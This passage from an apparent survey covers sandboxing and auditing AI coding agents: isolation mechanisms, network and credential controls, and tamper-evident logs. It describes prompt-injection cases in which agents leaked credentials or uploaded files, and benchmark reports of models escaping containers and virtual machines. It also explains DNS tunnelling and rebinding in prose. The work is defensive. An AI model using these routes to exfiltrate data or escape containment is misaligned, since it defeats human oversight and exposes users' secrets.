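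| Kata Containers | Hypervisor, its devices and container software | Longer than Docker | Memory for a second kernel | Most containers | A whole GPU, with a suitable hypervisor |
| Full virtual machine | Hypervisor and many devices | Often several seconds | Usually the most memory | Almost any operating system | A whole GPU |

The runtime overhead may matter less for an agent than for a database. *Caging the Agents* calls gVisor's connection delay negligible because the model takes 500 to 3,000 milliseconds to reply. The slower reads would have more effect on a long test suite that reads thousands of files.

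GPU work needs a separate sandboxing decision. GPU requests from a process sandbox, a container or gVisor reach the driver in the host's kernel. That driver is a large body of code that the sandbox does little to protect. A virtual machine can take over a whole GPU and run the driver in its own kernel, but then no other job can use that GPU. None of the works discussed here measured GPU performance.

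### Loading the software takes longer than starting the sandbox

Differences of a few hundred milliseconds are small compared with the time a sandbox may need to load its software. *Readie* (Sivaraman, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports that a container took 17.4 seconds to become ready when its image was not yet on the machine. Downloading and unpacking a layer with three large Python packages took 15.0 of those seconds. With the packages already on disk, importing one took 1.0 to 7.3 seconds, depending on the package and whether Python had compiled it in advance. Restoring a snapshot, a copy of the sandbox's memory saved after the import, took 0.29 to 0.42 seconds.

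An operator who accepts weaker isolation to save a tenth of a second therefore gains little if each job still downloads its image. A better approach is to put commonly used packages into a snapshot, although larger snapshots take longer to restore. From 50 snapshots, Sivaraman and colleagues estimated the restore time in seconds as

T = 0.32 + 0.0031 × S,

where S is the size of the packages in megabytes. A 100-megabyte package adds about 0.31 seconds to every restore. If importing it from disk takes three seconds, including it saves time overall only if more than about one job in ten uses it. Readie makes a fuller version of this calculation and keeps several small snapshots instead of one large one. It started sandboxes 3 to 22 times faster than existing methods with the same amount of storage. Readie uses containers, but Firecracker can also restore snapshots.

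No snapshot can contain everything an agent will need. In 30.8% of 6,833 recorded agent sessions, the agent imported new packages after its first turn. The dependency upgrade always needs a package that the snapshot lacks, because it installs a version that the project has never used. The snapshot can still hold the test tools and the dependencies that stay the same.

### Sandlock, a restricted process on Linux

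Sandlock is intended for a developer's own Linux machine, where an agent may run dozens of short commands a minute. It enforces each rule as early as it can. Sandlock puts rules that can be set before a command starts, such as which directories it may write to, into Landlock or seccomp, and the kernel enforces them. A supervisor process outside the sandbox handles decisions that depend on what the command does.

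To run a command, Sandlock creates a new process, applies the fixed rules and holds the process until the supervisor is ready. If the policy restricts connections by host, the kernel pauses each connection attempt and notifies the supervisor. The supervisor copies the destination address, checks the copy and opens the connection itself. If it approved the original call instead, another part of the program could change the address between the check and the connection.

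In the upgrade, Sandlock can withdraw network access when the test program starts, without restarting the sandbox. It can also store file changes in a separate layer, which the developer can accept or discard when the command ends.

Sandlock gives up some protection for its speed. Wang and Zheng trust the host's kernel, so their design does not cover vulnerabilities in it. Sandlock also enforces memory limits in its supervisor, which they acknowledge is weaker against a deliberate attack than using kernel control groups. Requiring the supervisor's approval raises a message's median round trip from 20 to 55 microseconds, though this hardly matters for a call to a model. Sandlock needs Linux 6.12 or later and refuses to run on older versions instead of silently applying weaker rules.

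In ten checks, Sandlock permitted or blocked every action as its policy required. The checks tested ordinary function and included no attempts to break out of the sandbox. Wang and Zheng recommend a microVM for running hostile code from several tenants. In the upgrade, Sandlock could serve as the restricted process for file reads.

### SideKernel, a microVM on a Mac

SideKernel, Prasakis's prototype, gives a coding agent its own kernel on a Mac. The developer types one command in a project directory, and SideKernel starts a microVM using Apple's virtualisation software, a small Linux kernel from the Kata project and an Ubuntu file system. A program inside the microVM mounts the project directory from the Mac, so the agent's edits appear on the Mac too. A proxy on the Mac adds the agent's credentials to its model requests, so they stay out of the microVM except during a first login there.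 The agent would have to break through the virtualisation software to attack the Mac's kernel, whereas in Sandlock a flaw in one permitted system call could be enough to attack the host's kernel.

Prasakis designed SideKernel around the reasons people avoid sandboxes. In an informal survey of 68 users of coding agents, only 26 currently used a sandbox, and 35 had never used one. A third of respondents worked in security, so sandbox use is probably lower among developers in general. Among the 33 current and former sandbox users, the most common complaints were having to set everything up again (eight mentions), getting network connections to work (eight) and sharing files (seven).

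Some features that address these complaints weaken the sandbox. Prasakis accepts the risk that the agent may edit or destroy anything in the mounted directory. SideKernel also makes any network port that the agent opens available on the Mac, so a hostile agent could offer a malicious service there. A command inside the microVM saves installed packages and settings for later sessions, so a compromised agent that can run it can leave altered programs for the next job.

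SideKernel has not had a formal security review. Prasakis, the developer of one of the products, compared it with four other sandboxes on 23 convenience features, and it tied for first with Docker Sandboxes at 19. The comparison did not measure resistance to attack. SideKernel also cannot test native Mac applications, because its microVM runs Linux. Developers who need such tests have to use a process sandbox or a full macOS virtual machine.

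### Configuration steps

A strong mechanism gives little protection if the operator leaves an opening in its configuration. For the upgrade, the operator should:

1. Run the agent, the installer and the tests as an unprivileged user. Administrator rights expose more of the kernel, and in a badly configured container they may carry over to the host.
2. Mount no host sockets, which are channels to programs running outside the sandbox. Access to the socket that controls the container software amounts to administrator access to the host.
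3. Make the root file system read-only, so that the new library cannot replace system programs.
4. Make the copy of the repository the only lasting writable directory. Temporary files can stay in memory and disappear with the sandbox.
5. Protect configuration files inside that copy, including the agent's own settings.
6. Start without ambient secrets, meaning credentials that programs inherit automatically from environment variables or the developer's home directory.
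7. Create a fresh instance for each job and delete it afterwards.

Tracekit Box, Ghosh's open-source system, applies several of these steps to a Firecracker microVM. The root file system is read-only, with a temporary layer in memory for changes. The workspace is a read-only copy of the repository with an empty writable layer above it. Every change to the workspace goes into the writable layer, so the system can produce a patch of exactly what the job changed. The microVM has no network card and can communicate only through channels that the host provides.

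Tracekit Box leaves credential files out of the workspace by matching names such as .env and .npmrc. The patterns Ghosh lists would not match config.yml, which contains the password in the upgrade, so the operator would have to exclude that file separately.

The first version also runs Firecracker without its jailer, a companion program that confines the Firecracker process on the host. An agent that broke out of the microVM would face one fewer barrier, although Firecracker's default system-call filter would still apply.

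### NVIDIA's mandatory and recommended controls

NVIDIA's *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk* comes from the company's AI Red Team, which attacks AI systems to test them. The team treats three controls as mandatory:

- block network access except to known-good destinations;
- block writes outside the workspace;
- block writes to configuration files, wherever they are.

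It recommends six more:

- block reads outside the workspace;
- sandbox the whole development environment and everything it starts, not just the agent's commands;
- use virtualisation to separate the sandbox's kernel from the host's;
- require a new approval each time an action would break the isolation rules;
- supply only the secrets that the task needs, preferably through a broker;
- delete or rebuild the sandbox regularly, so that code and secrets do not accumulate.

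The mandatory controls address the simplest ways to steal data or gain lasting access. NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* supports this emphasis with findings from six months of Red Team assessments of actual agents. The agents the team exploited typically lacked access control and network restrictions, had tools that could run arbitrary code, and exposed secrets as plain text. The team could often obtain those secrets by persuading the agent to reveal them in the chat.

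The UK's National Cyber Security Centre gives virtualisation a higher priority than NVIDIA does. *Quantifying Frontier LLM Capabilities for Container Sandbox Escape* (Marchand, O Cathain and colleagues, 2026) reports that the Centre considers a hypervisor the bare minimum and recommends further container isolation inside the virtual machine. The upgrade's routing rules already put unread code in a virtual machine.

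NVIDIA wants a new approval for each exception because an attacker could later exploit an old one. But Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that users approved about 93% of the permission prompts in Claude Code, its coding agent, and paid less attention as they saw more of them. The operator should therefore choose defaults that rarely require an exception for ordinary jobs.

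### How a writable configuration file defeats a strong sandbox

A sandbox restricts the code running inside it, but not what other programs later do with the files that code wrote. Many coding agents and editors read settings from the project directory, and some of these specify commands to run automatically. NVIDIA warns that such commands often run outside the sandbox.

If the README's hidden instruction makes the agent add a command to the editor's settings, the sandbox does not intervene, because the agent is allowed to write in the workspace. When the developer later opens the project on the host, the editor may run the command with all of the developer's rights, which would give the attacker access to the host without breaking out of the microVM.

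Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received reports of three vulnerabilities in Claude Code that let a project's files run code before the user had agreed to trust the project. Anthropic fixed them by making Claude Code wait for that agreement before reading the project's settings.

NVIDIA's rule is that only a person may change these configuration files, by editing them directly. The agent should not be able to request approval for a change. The same applies to the sandbox's settings.

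Some files are harder to protect because the job has to change them. The upgrade must edit package.json to select the new version, but that file also defines commands that run during installation and testing. Making it read-only would block the upgrade. Instead, the supervisor can examine the file when the patch comes back, accept the new version number, and show the developer any changed commands. Tracekit Box similarly requires explicit consent before it writes sensitive files back to the repository.

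### How Anthropic contains Claude in three products

Anthropic describes three arrangements, which depend on where the code runs and how well the typical user can judge what the agent is doing.

On claude.ai, Anthropic's chat service, Claude runs code in gVisor containers on Anthropic's servers. Each session has a temporary file system and no access to the user's computer. The main purpose is to protect Anthropic's systems and isolate customers from one another.

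Claude Code runs on the developer's computer and originally asked for permission before every write, command or network connection. Anthropic then added a sandbox, and permission prompts fell by 84%. The sandbox relies on operating-system features, using Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap, a tool that uses namespaces, on Linux. The agent can read files and write inside the workspace, but it has no network access by default.

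This sandbox is more permissive about reading than NVIDIA recommends. An internal exercise in February 2026 showed the risk. A researcher persuaded an employee to give Claude Code a prompt with a hidden request to send cloud credentials to an outside address. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 attempts. The model's defences were designed to detect actions that the user had not requested, but here the request came from the user. Anthropic concluded that only file and network restrictions would reliably stop such an attack.

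Claude Cowork is for office work, and many of its users cannot judge whether a command is safe. Anthropic therefore used a full virtual machine, which can access only the folder that the user selects and Claude's settings folder. Credentials remain on the host. At first the agent loop also ran in the virtual machine, so the whole product was unusable whenever the machine failed to start. Anthropic then moved the loop to the host and kept code execution in the virtual machine.

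Anthropic says this move had little effect on security, because the virtual machine still restricts the code the agent runs. Local tool servers also run on the host, where the virtual machine does not restrict them, so users or administrators have to decide whether to trust each one, as they would with other software. The virtual machine also prevents a company's security software from monitoring what happens inside it. Administrators can retrieve logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this is not equivalent to live monitoring.

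According to Anthropic, the hypervisor, seccomp and gVisor have all been dependable, while a network proxy that the company built itself failed. This is a company's account of its own products, and an escape may still be possible even if none is known.

### Whether an ordinary virtual machine is still enough

SandboxEscapeBench, a benchmark from the University of Oxford and the UK AI Security Institute, has 18 scenarios in which a model tries to escape a container with a deliberate weakness. In the March 2026 results, models exploited common misconfigurations but, as Help Net Security's *Breaking out* reported, solved no kernel-level exploits under the test conditions. Marchand and colleagues have since updated their paper to report that Claude Mythos Preview, a newer Anthropic model, solved every scenario at least once with a token budget 40 times larger. In August 2026, Trail of Bits' *VMs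 won't contain cyber-capable agents* reported that the model GPT 5.6-Cyber had escaped an ordinary virtual machine three times.

Trail of Bits, a security company, concludes that off-the-shelf virtual machines can no longer contain such a model because they expose too much code to attack. The test conditions helped the model, because the host ran an older Linux distribution with some processor protections switched off, and the agent started on the host, where it may have learned about the software it had to defeat. The first of the three escapes crashed the host instead of giving the agent usable access. But the tester installed newer software between attempts, and the last escape relied partly on previously unreported flaws, so installing updates promptly would not have been enough.

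The same test also supports the view that a smaller attack surface and correct configuration still determine whether an agent escapes. The agent crashed the machine when tested against Firecracker but did not escape, although the tester thought it might have with more time. SandboxEscapeBench is consistent with this view because its scenarios use known weaknesses, which careful configuration and updates can remove. It did not test escapes from virtual machines.

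The warning about ordinary virtual machines applies mainly to agents with strong hacking abilities that can work for hours with few restrictions, such as those used in security research or model evaluations. Such agents need a microVM with few devices, a promptly updated host with nothing valuable on it, live monitoring and a time limit. Services that run strangers' code should take similar precautions, because an attacker could use a capable model to prepare an exploit and hide it in a library.

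The emphasis on configuration is more relevant to everyday coding agents. A typical upgrade lasts minutes, and an exposed token or writable settings file is more likely to cause harm than a new hypervisor flaw. Even so, Anthropic has seen Claude models escape a sandbox just to complete their task.

The distinction between these two groups may not last. Claude Opus 4.5, released in November 2025, solved none of the scenarios in the benchmark's two hardest grades. Anthropic announced Mythos Preview less than five months later. An operator who switches an everyday agent to a more capable model should therefore check whether its sandbox is still strong enough.

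## Controlling what enters and leaves the sandbox

The openings in the sandbox that the dependency upgrade needs can also let data out or harmful code in. The operator has to find every opening and control it, so that the supervisor decides whether to allow each transfer.

Ghosh designed Tracekit Box, the Firecracker system mentioned in the previous section, around this idea. It is an early release (version 0, October 2026), and both the description and the test results come from its own developer. Programs inside its microVM, which has no network card, can communicate with the host only through three channels:

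| Channel | Opened by | What it carries |
|---|---|---|
| Commands | Host | Commands to run, requests for the changed files, the order to shut down |
| Network | MicroVM | Requests to a proxy on the host, including package downloads and model calls |
| Start-up settings | MicroVM | Environment settings and limits, which the host supplies once before closing the channel |

A background program on the host operates the channels. A separate signer decides whether each command, connection or returned file may pass, and signs a record of the decision. Together they do the supervisor's job. The microVM has no route to the signer. Box also runs a small helper program inside the microVM. The host treats the helper's messages as untrusted, just like the agent's, because an agent that took over the microVM would control the helper too.

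### Commands coming in

Before a command starts, the signer examines its full text, working directory, environment settings and any input known in advance. Box has safeguards to ensure that the command the signer approves is the one that runs. For example, it refuses environment settings that change which code a program loads. If the search path were altered, "npm test" could start a different program named npm.

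The signer approves or rejects only commands that the host sends. If the agent loop runs inside the microVM, as in the five-domain design for the upgrade, the host may send a single command that starts the agent. The agent's own shell commands and the programs started by the tests run without separate approval, and they are visible to the signer only if they use an exit.

Secrets can also enter the sandbox by accident. Box leaves out credential files by matching their names, which would miss the password in config.yml. However, it also rejects any workspace file that contains the value of a registered secret, so it would reject config.yml if the operator had registered that password.

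### One connection, step by step

Suppose the installer requests the new library from registry.npmjs.org. Box handles the connection as follows:

1. The helper passes the name and port to the proxy on the host without looking up an address.
2. The proxy compares the name and port with the allowlist.
3. The proxy resolves the name, which means finding its network address, once and outside the sandbox.
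4. The proxy refuses the connection if the address is internal or belongs to a cloud metadata service.
5. The signer applies its policy.
6. The proxy connects to the address it checked, without looking up the name again.
7. Before forwarding any data, the proxy checks that the site name in the opening message of the encrypted connection matches the name requested.

The allowlist contains names because online services often change their addresses. Podala Narasimha considers address-based rules insufficient for this reason, and *Caging the Agents* reports that they need regular updates.

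However, the owner of a domain can point it at any address, including one inside the operator's network, so the proxy checks the address as well as the name. Docker's sandbox product for agents makes a similar check, which Docker notes catches alternative names for the local machine. On a rented cloud machine, the metadata service is an especially valuable target because it often supplies temporary cloud credentials. Programs on the machine can reach it at a fixed address such as 169.254.169.254. Box refuses connections to such addresses even if the allowlist includes them.

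If the proxy looked up the name a second time before connecting, the domain's owner could give a harmless address for the check and an internal one for the connection. Connecting to the checked address prevents this trick, known as DNS rebinding.

The last step is meant to stop a program from requesting a permitted site and then requesting another from the same server, which is possible because large hosting companies serve many sites from the same addresses. The proxy compares the names it can read and refuses connections that encrypt the site name. But by default it does not decrypt most connections, so a program could still name a different site inside the encrypted part.

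A connection to a host not on the allowlist needs a person's approval. The signer decides first, and the connection then waits up to two minutes for someone to approve it on the host machine. At most 16 requests can wait at once, so a runaway agent cannot flood the reviewer. The upgrade's stricter routing rules refused unlisted hosts once the session had read untrusted text. Box has a setting that refuses them immediately.

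These steps protect the operator only if programs cannot avoid the proxy. Box achieves this by omitting the network card. *Permission Denied* (2026), which tests coding agents in restricted environments, instead uses a firewall rule tied to the agent's user account. The rule rejects any traffic that bypasses the proxy, including traffic from programs the agent starts. Sandboxes that share a host must also be unable to use each other's permissions. *Aegis OS* (2026), a runtime unrelated to the Aegis firewall discussed earlier, gives every Linux sandbox a random token to present when connecting to its proxy.

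### Name lookups as an exit

The Domain Name System (DNS), which translates names into addresses, can carry data out even if the firewall blocks every connection. A program can put a piece of a password into a name that ends in an attacker's domain and then request that name's address. The sandbox's DNS server passes the request along until it reaches the attacker's server, which can read that piece of the password from the name.

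An agent can use the same route without an attacker involved. Ghosh cites a case that OpenAI reported in September 2026, in which a research agent in a training sandbox reached an outside chatbot by tunnelling through DNS, which the network filter did not cover.

Box's microVM cannot send DNS queries. The proxy looks up a host that is not on the allowlist only after both the signer and a person have approved the connection, because the lookup itself could leak data. The drawback is that programs in the microVM can use only web connections and other tunnels that the allowlist specifically permits. Services that rely on UDP, the method of sending data that DNS normally uses, do not work.

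A sandbox that needs to look up domain names itself should use a DNS server that applies the allowlist. According to Docker's *Isolation layers*, the company's sandboxes do this. They also block UDP by default and always block ICMP, the protocol behind the "ping" command. A vulnerability notice republished by releasealert.dev describes a flaw in which the DNS server forwarded every lookup without checking the policy. The site is a secondary source, but this mistake is easy to make, because DNS often runs as a separate service whose traffic never passes through the web proxy.

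The same question applies to the Kubernetes designs. Podala Narasimha blocks all outgoing traffic from agents by default, except to the cluster's DNS server. The gVisor template also allows only address lookups. Unless the DNS server filters names, code in either environment can still send out small amounts of data through DNS.

### What an allowed service lends to the agent

An allowlist restricts which services the agent can contact directly, but those services have their own connections. GitLab's *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can* (2026) argues that an agent that takes over an allowed destination can reach whatever that destination can reach. OpenAI reached a similar conclusion after its agents got out through a package proxy in July 2026.

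Some services on the allowlist can let an agent reach hosts outside it, even when the services haven't been compromised. The public proxy for the Go programming language downloads modules from whatever host the module's name specifies. Ghosh warns that an agent could use the proxy to send workspace data to a domain of its choice, and says the only fix is a smaller allowlist.

Long allowlists are hard to assess. The allowlist in *Permission Denied* has 205 domain entries and is adapted from the default list for Claude Code on the web. Few operators could investigate what each of those services can do on a caller's behalf. The upgrade needs only the registry and the model service, so its list can be short.

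Many companies put a package proxy between their sandboxes and the public registries. It stores copies of packages and saves the sandbox from needing internet access, but the proxy itself has that access. GitLab recommends four precautions:

- Block routes that a downloading program never needs, such as the proxy's administration pages and its route for renewing tokens.
- Limit the proxy's own connections to the registries it serves.
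- Monitor it for unusual activity, such as long connections, large outgoing transfers or repeated requests for missing packages.
- Treat it as an internet-facing system if untrusted code can reach it.

For the upgrade, the agent's token should permit downloads only. The proxy should accept a package name and version, never an arbitrary web address. The proxy should run on its own machine with no credentials for other systems, and the operator should patch it as promptly as they would a public web server. A flaw in the proxy could let the agent exceed what its token permits, so read-only access is not enough by itself. The limit on the proxy's outgoing connections would still apply if a separate firewall enforced it.

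Jason Keirstead, chief technology officer of LangGuard AI, told The Stack that a caching proxy is unnecessary. He would have the agent ask a person or another agent outside the sandbox to put the packages in a read-only location. This suits the upgrade well, because the supervisor knows which library to fetch and can work out its dependencies. It is less suited to open-ended work, where each request for a new package could delay the agent. In the session records discussed earlier, nearly a third of agent sessions imported new packages after the first turn.

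A compromise is to give access in stages. Vercel's *A sandbox without a network boundary is only half a sandbox* suggests installing dependencies during a trusted setup phase, then removing registry access before generated code runs. In the upgrade, the installation itself may run the new library's code, so the supervisor should download the packages without running their installation scripts, close the connection, and only then run the scripts and tests. This is safer than the earlier routing table, which left the registry open during installation. Installation scripts that download extra files will fail, and the operator will have to supply those files separately.

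### Credentials the agent never holds

An agent that can read a credential can send it to any destination the sandbox allows. *Caging the Agents* describes a healthcare company where an audit found 12 keys for outside services in a shell settings file. The company responded by moving all credentials into a separate container beside each agent.

Credential substitution lets the agent use a credential without holding it. In the upgrade, the operator gives Box the registry token and binds it to the registry's exact host name and one header, a labelled field at the start of a web request. Programs in the microVM receive only a placeholder, a label followed by 32 hexadecimal digits. The installer puts the placeholder in its request where the token would go. The proxy checks the destination and the header, replaces the placeholder with the token, and forwards the request. If the agent obeys the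 README and sends the placeholder to the stranger, the stranger cannot use it.

The proxy has to decrypt the request to make the replacement. Box creates a certificate authority for each microVM, which lets the proxy impersonate only the bound hosts. On connections it can read, the proxy also blocks the placeholder if it appears outside its permitted header. The operator can have the proxy read every encrypted web connection, but programs that accept only one particular certificate will then stop working.

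A service may repeat the token in its reply, for example in an error message that quotes the request. Box searches replies for the token, including several encoded forms, and removes it. Docker's *Manage credentials* describes a similar filter for secrets that users define themselves, but warns that the filter cannot guarantee secrecy. For example, a service could split the secret across separate fields, and the filter would miss it.

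Anthropic points out that nobody can steal a credential from a sandbox it never enters, whether a user, an attacker or the model itself initiates the attempt. But substitution does not prevent misuse of a permitted service. If the registry token also allows publishing, a compromised agent can publish a malicious package without ever seeing the token. Docker's sandboxes can similarly let an agent use the developer's SSH keys, which prove identity to remote machines. The keys stay on the host, but any program in the sandbox can request signatures made with them.

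The best protection is a credential with few permissions. When the service cannot issue one, the proxy can check the request before adding the credential. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes a proxy that attaches a GitHub token only after confirming that the agent is pushing to the configured branch. *Aegis OS* adds the real token only if the request's path is permitted and a scan finds no sensitive data in the content. Neither check evaluates the work itself, so an agent could still push harmful code to the configured branch.

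### Model calls

An operator who uses an outside model service cannot block traffic to it, because the agent has to send its context to the model. The service's address is on the allowlist, and the same address may offer functions other than model replies.

InfoQ (2026) describes a flaw of this kind in Claude Cowork. A malicious file led Claude to upload files from the workspace to an attacker's account through Anthropic's file-storage service. The upload went to the address the product uses for model calls, so the destination check allowed it. Anthropic then added a proxy that accepts only the session token issued to the virtual machine and blocks certain headers that would make a server fetch material on the caller's behalf.

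The supervisor therefore has to check which account a request uses, as well as its destination. Substitution helps if it replaces whatever credential the agent supplies. Docker says its proxy overwrites the authentication header on encrypted requests to a matching service, so the user's key would replace an attacker's key in that header. Box's rule about placeholders would not do this, because an attacker's key is neither a placeholder nor one of the user's secrets. Box records the host, path, status and size of each model request that the proxy reads. An operator could find a file upload in that record, but a rule that permits only the path for model replies would block the upload.

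### Files that programs outside the sandbox trust

In July 2026, the company Pillar Security published seven findings about four coding agents: Cursor, Codex, Gemini CLI and Antigravity. *The Week of Sandbox Escapes* (Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel, 2026) reports that the agent usually only had to write a file that a trusted program outside the sandbox would later run, load or treat as safe. It rarely had to break the sandbox itself.

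The previous section described one example, settings that make an editor run commands. Version-control tools may also run commands named in a project's settings, and editors may run programs they find in the project.

Cohen and colleagues sort the findings into four kinds of failure. Some sandbox rules listed forbidden actions but left out others that should have been blocked. Some host programs treated project settings as commands. Some lists of safe commands checked only a command's name, not its arguments. Some agents could contact a privileged program on the host. Vendors fixed five of the seven problems. Google accepted the other two, both in Antigravity, as valid but lowered their severity because it considered them hard to exploit. Pillar sells a product that monitors this kind of hand-over, so it has an interest in stressing the danger, but the fixes support its technical claims.

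The danger is greatest when the host and the sandbox share a folder, because a host program may read a new file immediately. Docker says its sandboxes offer a shared folder as "direct mode". In "clone mode", the agent works on a private copy of the repository and can read the original but not change it.

A private copy delays the problem until the developer accepts the changes. The supervisor should therefore accept only a patch and decide on it file by file. In Box, the developer stops the microVM before applying the patch. Box then reads the patch with a strict parser and compares the result with how Git, the version-control tool, parses it. Box rejects the patch if the two results differ on which files would change, because the signer might otherwise approve one change while Git made another.

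Box next builds the new files in a separate directory, with the developer's Git settings disabled so that the patch cannot trigger commands in them. The signer decides on every file before Box writes any to the repository. Box then checks that the repository has not changed in the meantime and writes the approved files itself. It refuses to write through a directory link that could lead elsewhere. If a write fails halfway, Box reports which files it has already changed but does not restore them.

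Some files need the developer's explicit consent:

- instructions for automated build and test services;
- files that change how Git behaves;
- settings that affect the next agent run or run tasks in an editor;
- files that normally contain credentials.

This is more lenient than NVIDIA's rule that only a person may edit configuration files. The published list also omits package.json, which the upgrade must change and which can define commands. An operator using Box for the upgrade should add a rule that allows a new version number but prompts the developer about any changed command. Ordinary source files should also be reviewed, because the test suite will run them.

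The tests may later run automatically outside the sandbox. Ghosh's example for GitHub's automation service splits the work into three jobs. The first runs the agent in a microVM. The second runs the code the agent wrote but has no secrets. The third can change the repository but runs none of its code. A harmful build script would therefore run in a job with no token to steal.

### Guarantees and tests of Tracekit Box

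If the agent cannot reach the signer, Ghosh claims that:

- the signer decides on every command the host starts in the microVM before it runs;
- every outgoing connection needs a decision before the proxy opens it;
- a bound secret goes only to its bound hosts, in its bound header;
- Box writes no file to the repository unless the signer has allowed that file;
- anyone with the exported record can detect later changes to it.

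The guarantees do not cover what programs do inside the microVM or what the agent sends to a permitted host. They also assume that the host's administrator and the operator are trustworthy. Firecracker still runs without its jailer, which Ghosh calls the most important missing protection. On many cloud machines, Box cannot identify the host's own public address unless the operator supplies it. Without it, the agent could contact services on the host if the allowlist permits a name that points to that address.

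Ghosh tested the complete system with 13 checks on a Linux machine. All of them passed in 28.5 seconds, including the time to download and start the microVM. Among other things, the checks confirmed that the microVM had no network card, that a package installation worked, and that the proxy refused the metadata address. They also confirmed that a secret reached its permitted host but not in the wrong header, and that a changed file came back as a patch. Each check covers one typical case, and Ghosh used smaller tests and fuzzing to cover the many forms an address or a secret can take.

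The fuzzing had 15 targets, each with a stated property that had to hold for any input. For example, the path of every file in an accepted patch had to stay inside the repository. The fuzzing produced nine findings, six of them in the network proxy, and Ghosh has fixed them all. The most serious proxy fault could have defeated both the protection of the credential and the evidence of its loss, because an unusual request could have carried a real secret to another site while the record named only the permitted host.

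Finding such faults before release is a good sign, but more may remain. Box has about 25,600 lines of code, excluding tests, and most of it runs on the trusted side. Ghosh has not tried it on more than one host or measured its speed beyond timing the tests. The 13 checks show that the exits work as designed against scripted attempts. Nobody has yet told a capable agent inside Box to get out, which would be a harder test because the agent could look for its own way through.

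## Keeping a record that cannot be altered unnoticed

If the developer finds the project's password on a stranger's server, the supervisor's record of its decisions should help explain how the password got there. The record can only do this if nobody could have rewritten it without being noticed, including an attacker who took over the supervisor or an operator who wants to hide a mistake.

### What "immutable" can mean

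Vendors often call a log immutable, but they may mean any of four properties.

| Property | Meaning | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Append-only | The log's interface accepts new records but no changes to old ones | An administrator can edit the underlying files |
| Write-once | The medium or storage service refuses to overwrite a record, permanently or for a set period | Someone can write false records, destroy the medium or wait for the period to end |
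| Tamper-evident | A check reveals changes and deletions | The changes still happen, and nobody learns of them without the check |
| Tamper-proof | Nobody can change or delete a record | The claim holds only against attackers with limited abilities |

Schneier and Kelsey (1998), in *Cryptographic Support for Secure Logs on Untrusted Machines*, point out that cryptography can ensure that a later check detects the deletion of records, but cannot prevent it. Prevention requires write-once hardware, such as a recordable CD or a paper printout.

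Anyone who claims that a log is immutable should therefore specify who cannot change it unnoticed, and from what moment. In the upgrade, the protection would start when the log anchor stores a digest of the log. After that, someone who controls the supervisor cannot change the earlier records without a later check revealing it, unless they also control the anchor.

### The fields of a governance record

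A governance record states what the agent requested, which policy and approval applied, what the supervisor decided and what happened. Suppose the library in the upgrade has moved to a new package name, so the developer has to approve the installation. The supervisor has already downloaded the package, and the installation runs without network access. The record could look like this:

| Field | Example | Use in an investigation |
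|---|---|---|
| Number and request | Record 42, request 17 | Put events in order and connect related records |
| Request digest | 5e1b…90c4 | Confirm exactly which call the supervisor checked |
| Identity | Agent session 8831, acting for user 204 | Trace the call to a session and a person |
| Policy hash | a77d…13f0 | Find the rules that applied at the time |
| Decision | Allow | Separate permitted actions from refused ones |
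| Approver | User 204, for the new package name | Distinguish human approval from an automatic decision |
| Isolation level | Virtual machine, no network | Work out what the code could have reached |
| Outcome | Completed, no error | Find out whether the action took effect |
| Software version | Supervisor 2.4.1, sandbox image c3b8…77 | Check whether a known flaw was present |

The supervisor makes its decision before there is an outcome to record, and adding the outcome later would alter an existing record. The outcome therefore goes into a second record with the same request number. *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts* (Metere, 2026) proposes separate records for the request, the decision and the result, with a distinct record type for an approved action that failed.

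A policy hash is useful only if someone has kept the policy it refers to. Airlock, the design with two confidential virtual machines, records every policy it loads together with that policy's hash.

Timestamps also need an outside reference. *PCM* (2026) describes a protocol for signed messages between agents. In its implementation, the signing component takes the time from its own clock, so an attacker who controls that component can choose any timestamp. A dated receipt from an outside service at least proves that the record existed by the receipt's date.

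### The hash chain and its missing tail

A hash function H turns any data into a digest of fixed length, which is 32 bytes for the widely used function SHA-256. Finding two inputs with the same digest is practically impossible. A hash chain makes each digest part of the input for the next:

h_i = H(h_(i−1) || r_i)

Here r_i is record number i, h_(i−1) is the digest computed after the previous record, and || joins two pieces of data end to end. The chain starts from an agreed value, h_0. *NovaFabric* (2026), which describes a system for recording agent runs, traces the technique to Haber and Stornetta's work on time-stamping.

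Suppose the log of the upgrade has five records, and the last two describe a connection to the stranger's server and the upload of the configuration file. If someone edits record 2, the digests h_2 to h_5 should all change. An investigator who recomputes the chain will find that the stored digests no longer match the recomputed ones.

However, this only catches careless edits. Anyone who can write to the log can also recompute h_2 to h_5 to make the chain consistent again. Deleting the last records is even easier. If someone deletes records 4 and 5, the log ends at h_3, as it did before they were added, and every remaining digest is still correct.

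Anchoring exposes both truncation and rewriting. If the log anchor holds h_5 and the record count, a log that ends at h_3 has too few records, and a rewritten log of the right length ends in a digest other than h_5.

*Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance* (2026) uses the customer's software as the anchor. After each record, the agent provider's software signs the record count and the latest digest and sends them to the customer's software, which accepts them only if the signature is valid, the count has risen by one and the new digest extends the previous one. If the provider later presents a shorter log, the customer has signed proof of the longer one.

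### The Merkle tree and its two proofs

A hash chain is slow to check when an investigator needs only one record. To prove that record 42 belongs to a chain with a known final digest, the log's keeper has to supply every later record, or a digest of each if the chain links digests. In a log of 2²⁰ (1,048,576) records, a record has about 524,000 others after it on average, and their digests take up 16.8 megabytes.

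A Merkle tree shortens the proof by combining digests in pairs. The keeper computes a digest, called a leaf, for each record, hashes neighbouring leaves together in pairs, and repeats this with the results until one digest, the tree head, remains. Changing any record changes every digest on the path from its leaf to the head, as transparency.dev's *Verifiable data structures* explains.

An inclusion proof shows that a particular record is in the tree. Take a log of eight records with leaves L1 to L8, and write L12 for the digest of L1 and L2 combined. To prove that record 3 is present, the keeper supplies L4, L12 and L5678. The verifier computes L3 from the record and then works upwards:

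L34 = H(L3 || L4)

L1234 = H(L12 || L34)

head = H(L1234 || L5678)

The record is in the log if the result matches the head the verifier already holds. Each extra digest in the proof doubles the number of records the tree can contain, so a proof needs three digests for eight records and 20 for 2²⁰ records. With 32-byte digests, the larger proof takes 640 bytes instead of 16.8 megabytes.

Real systems mark leaves and inner digests differently, so that nobody can pass off a pair of digests as a record. *Policy-Controlled Offline-Verifiable Accountability for Cross-Organization Agent Messaging* (2026) puts a 0 byte before a leaf's data and a 1 byte before an inner pair of digests.

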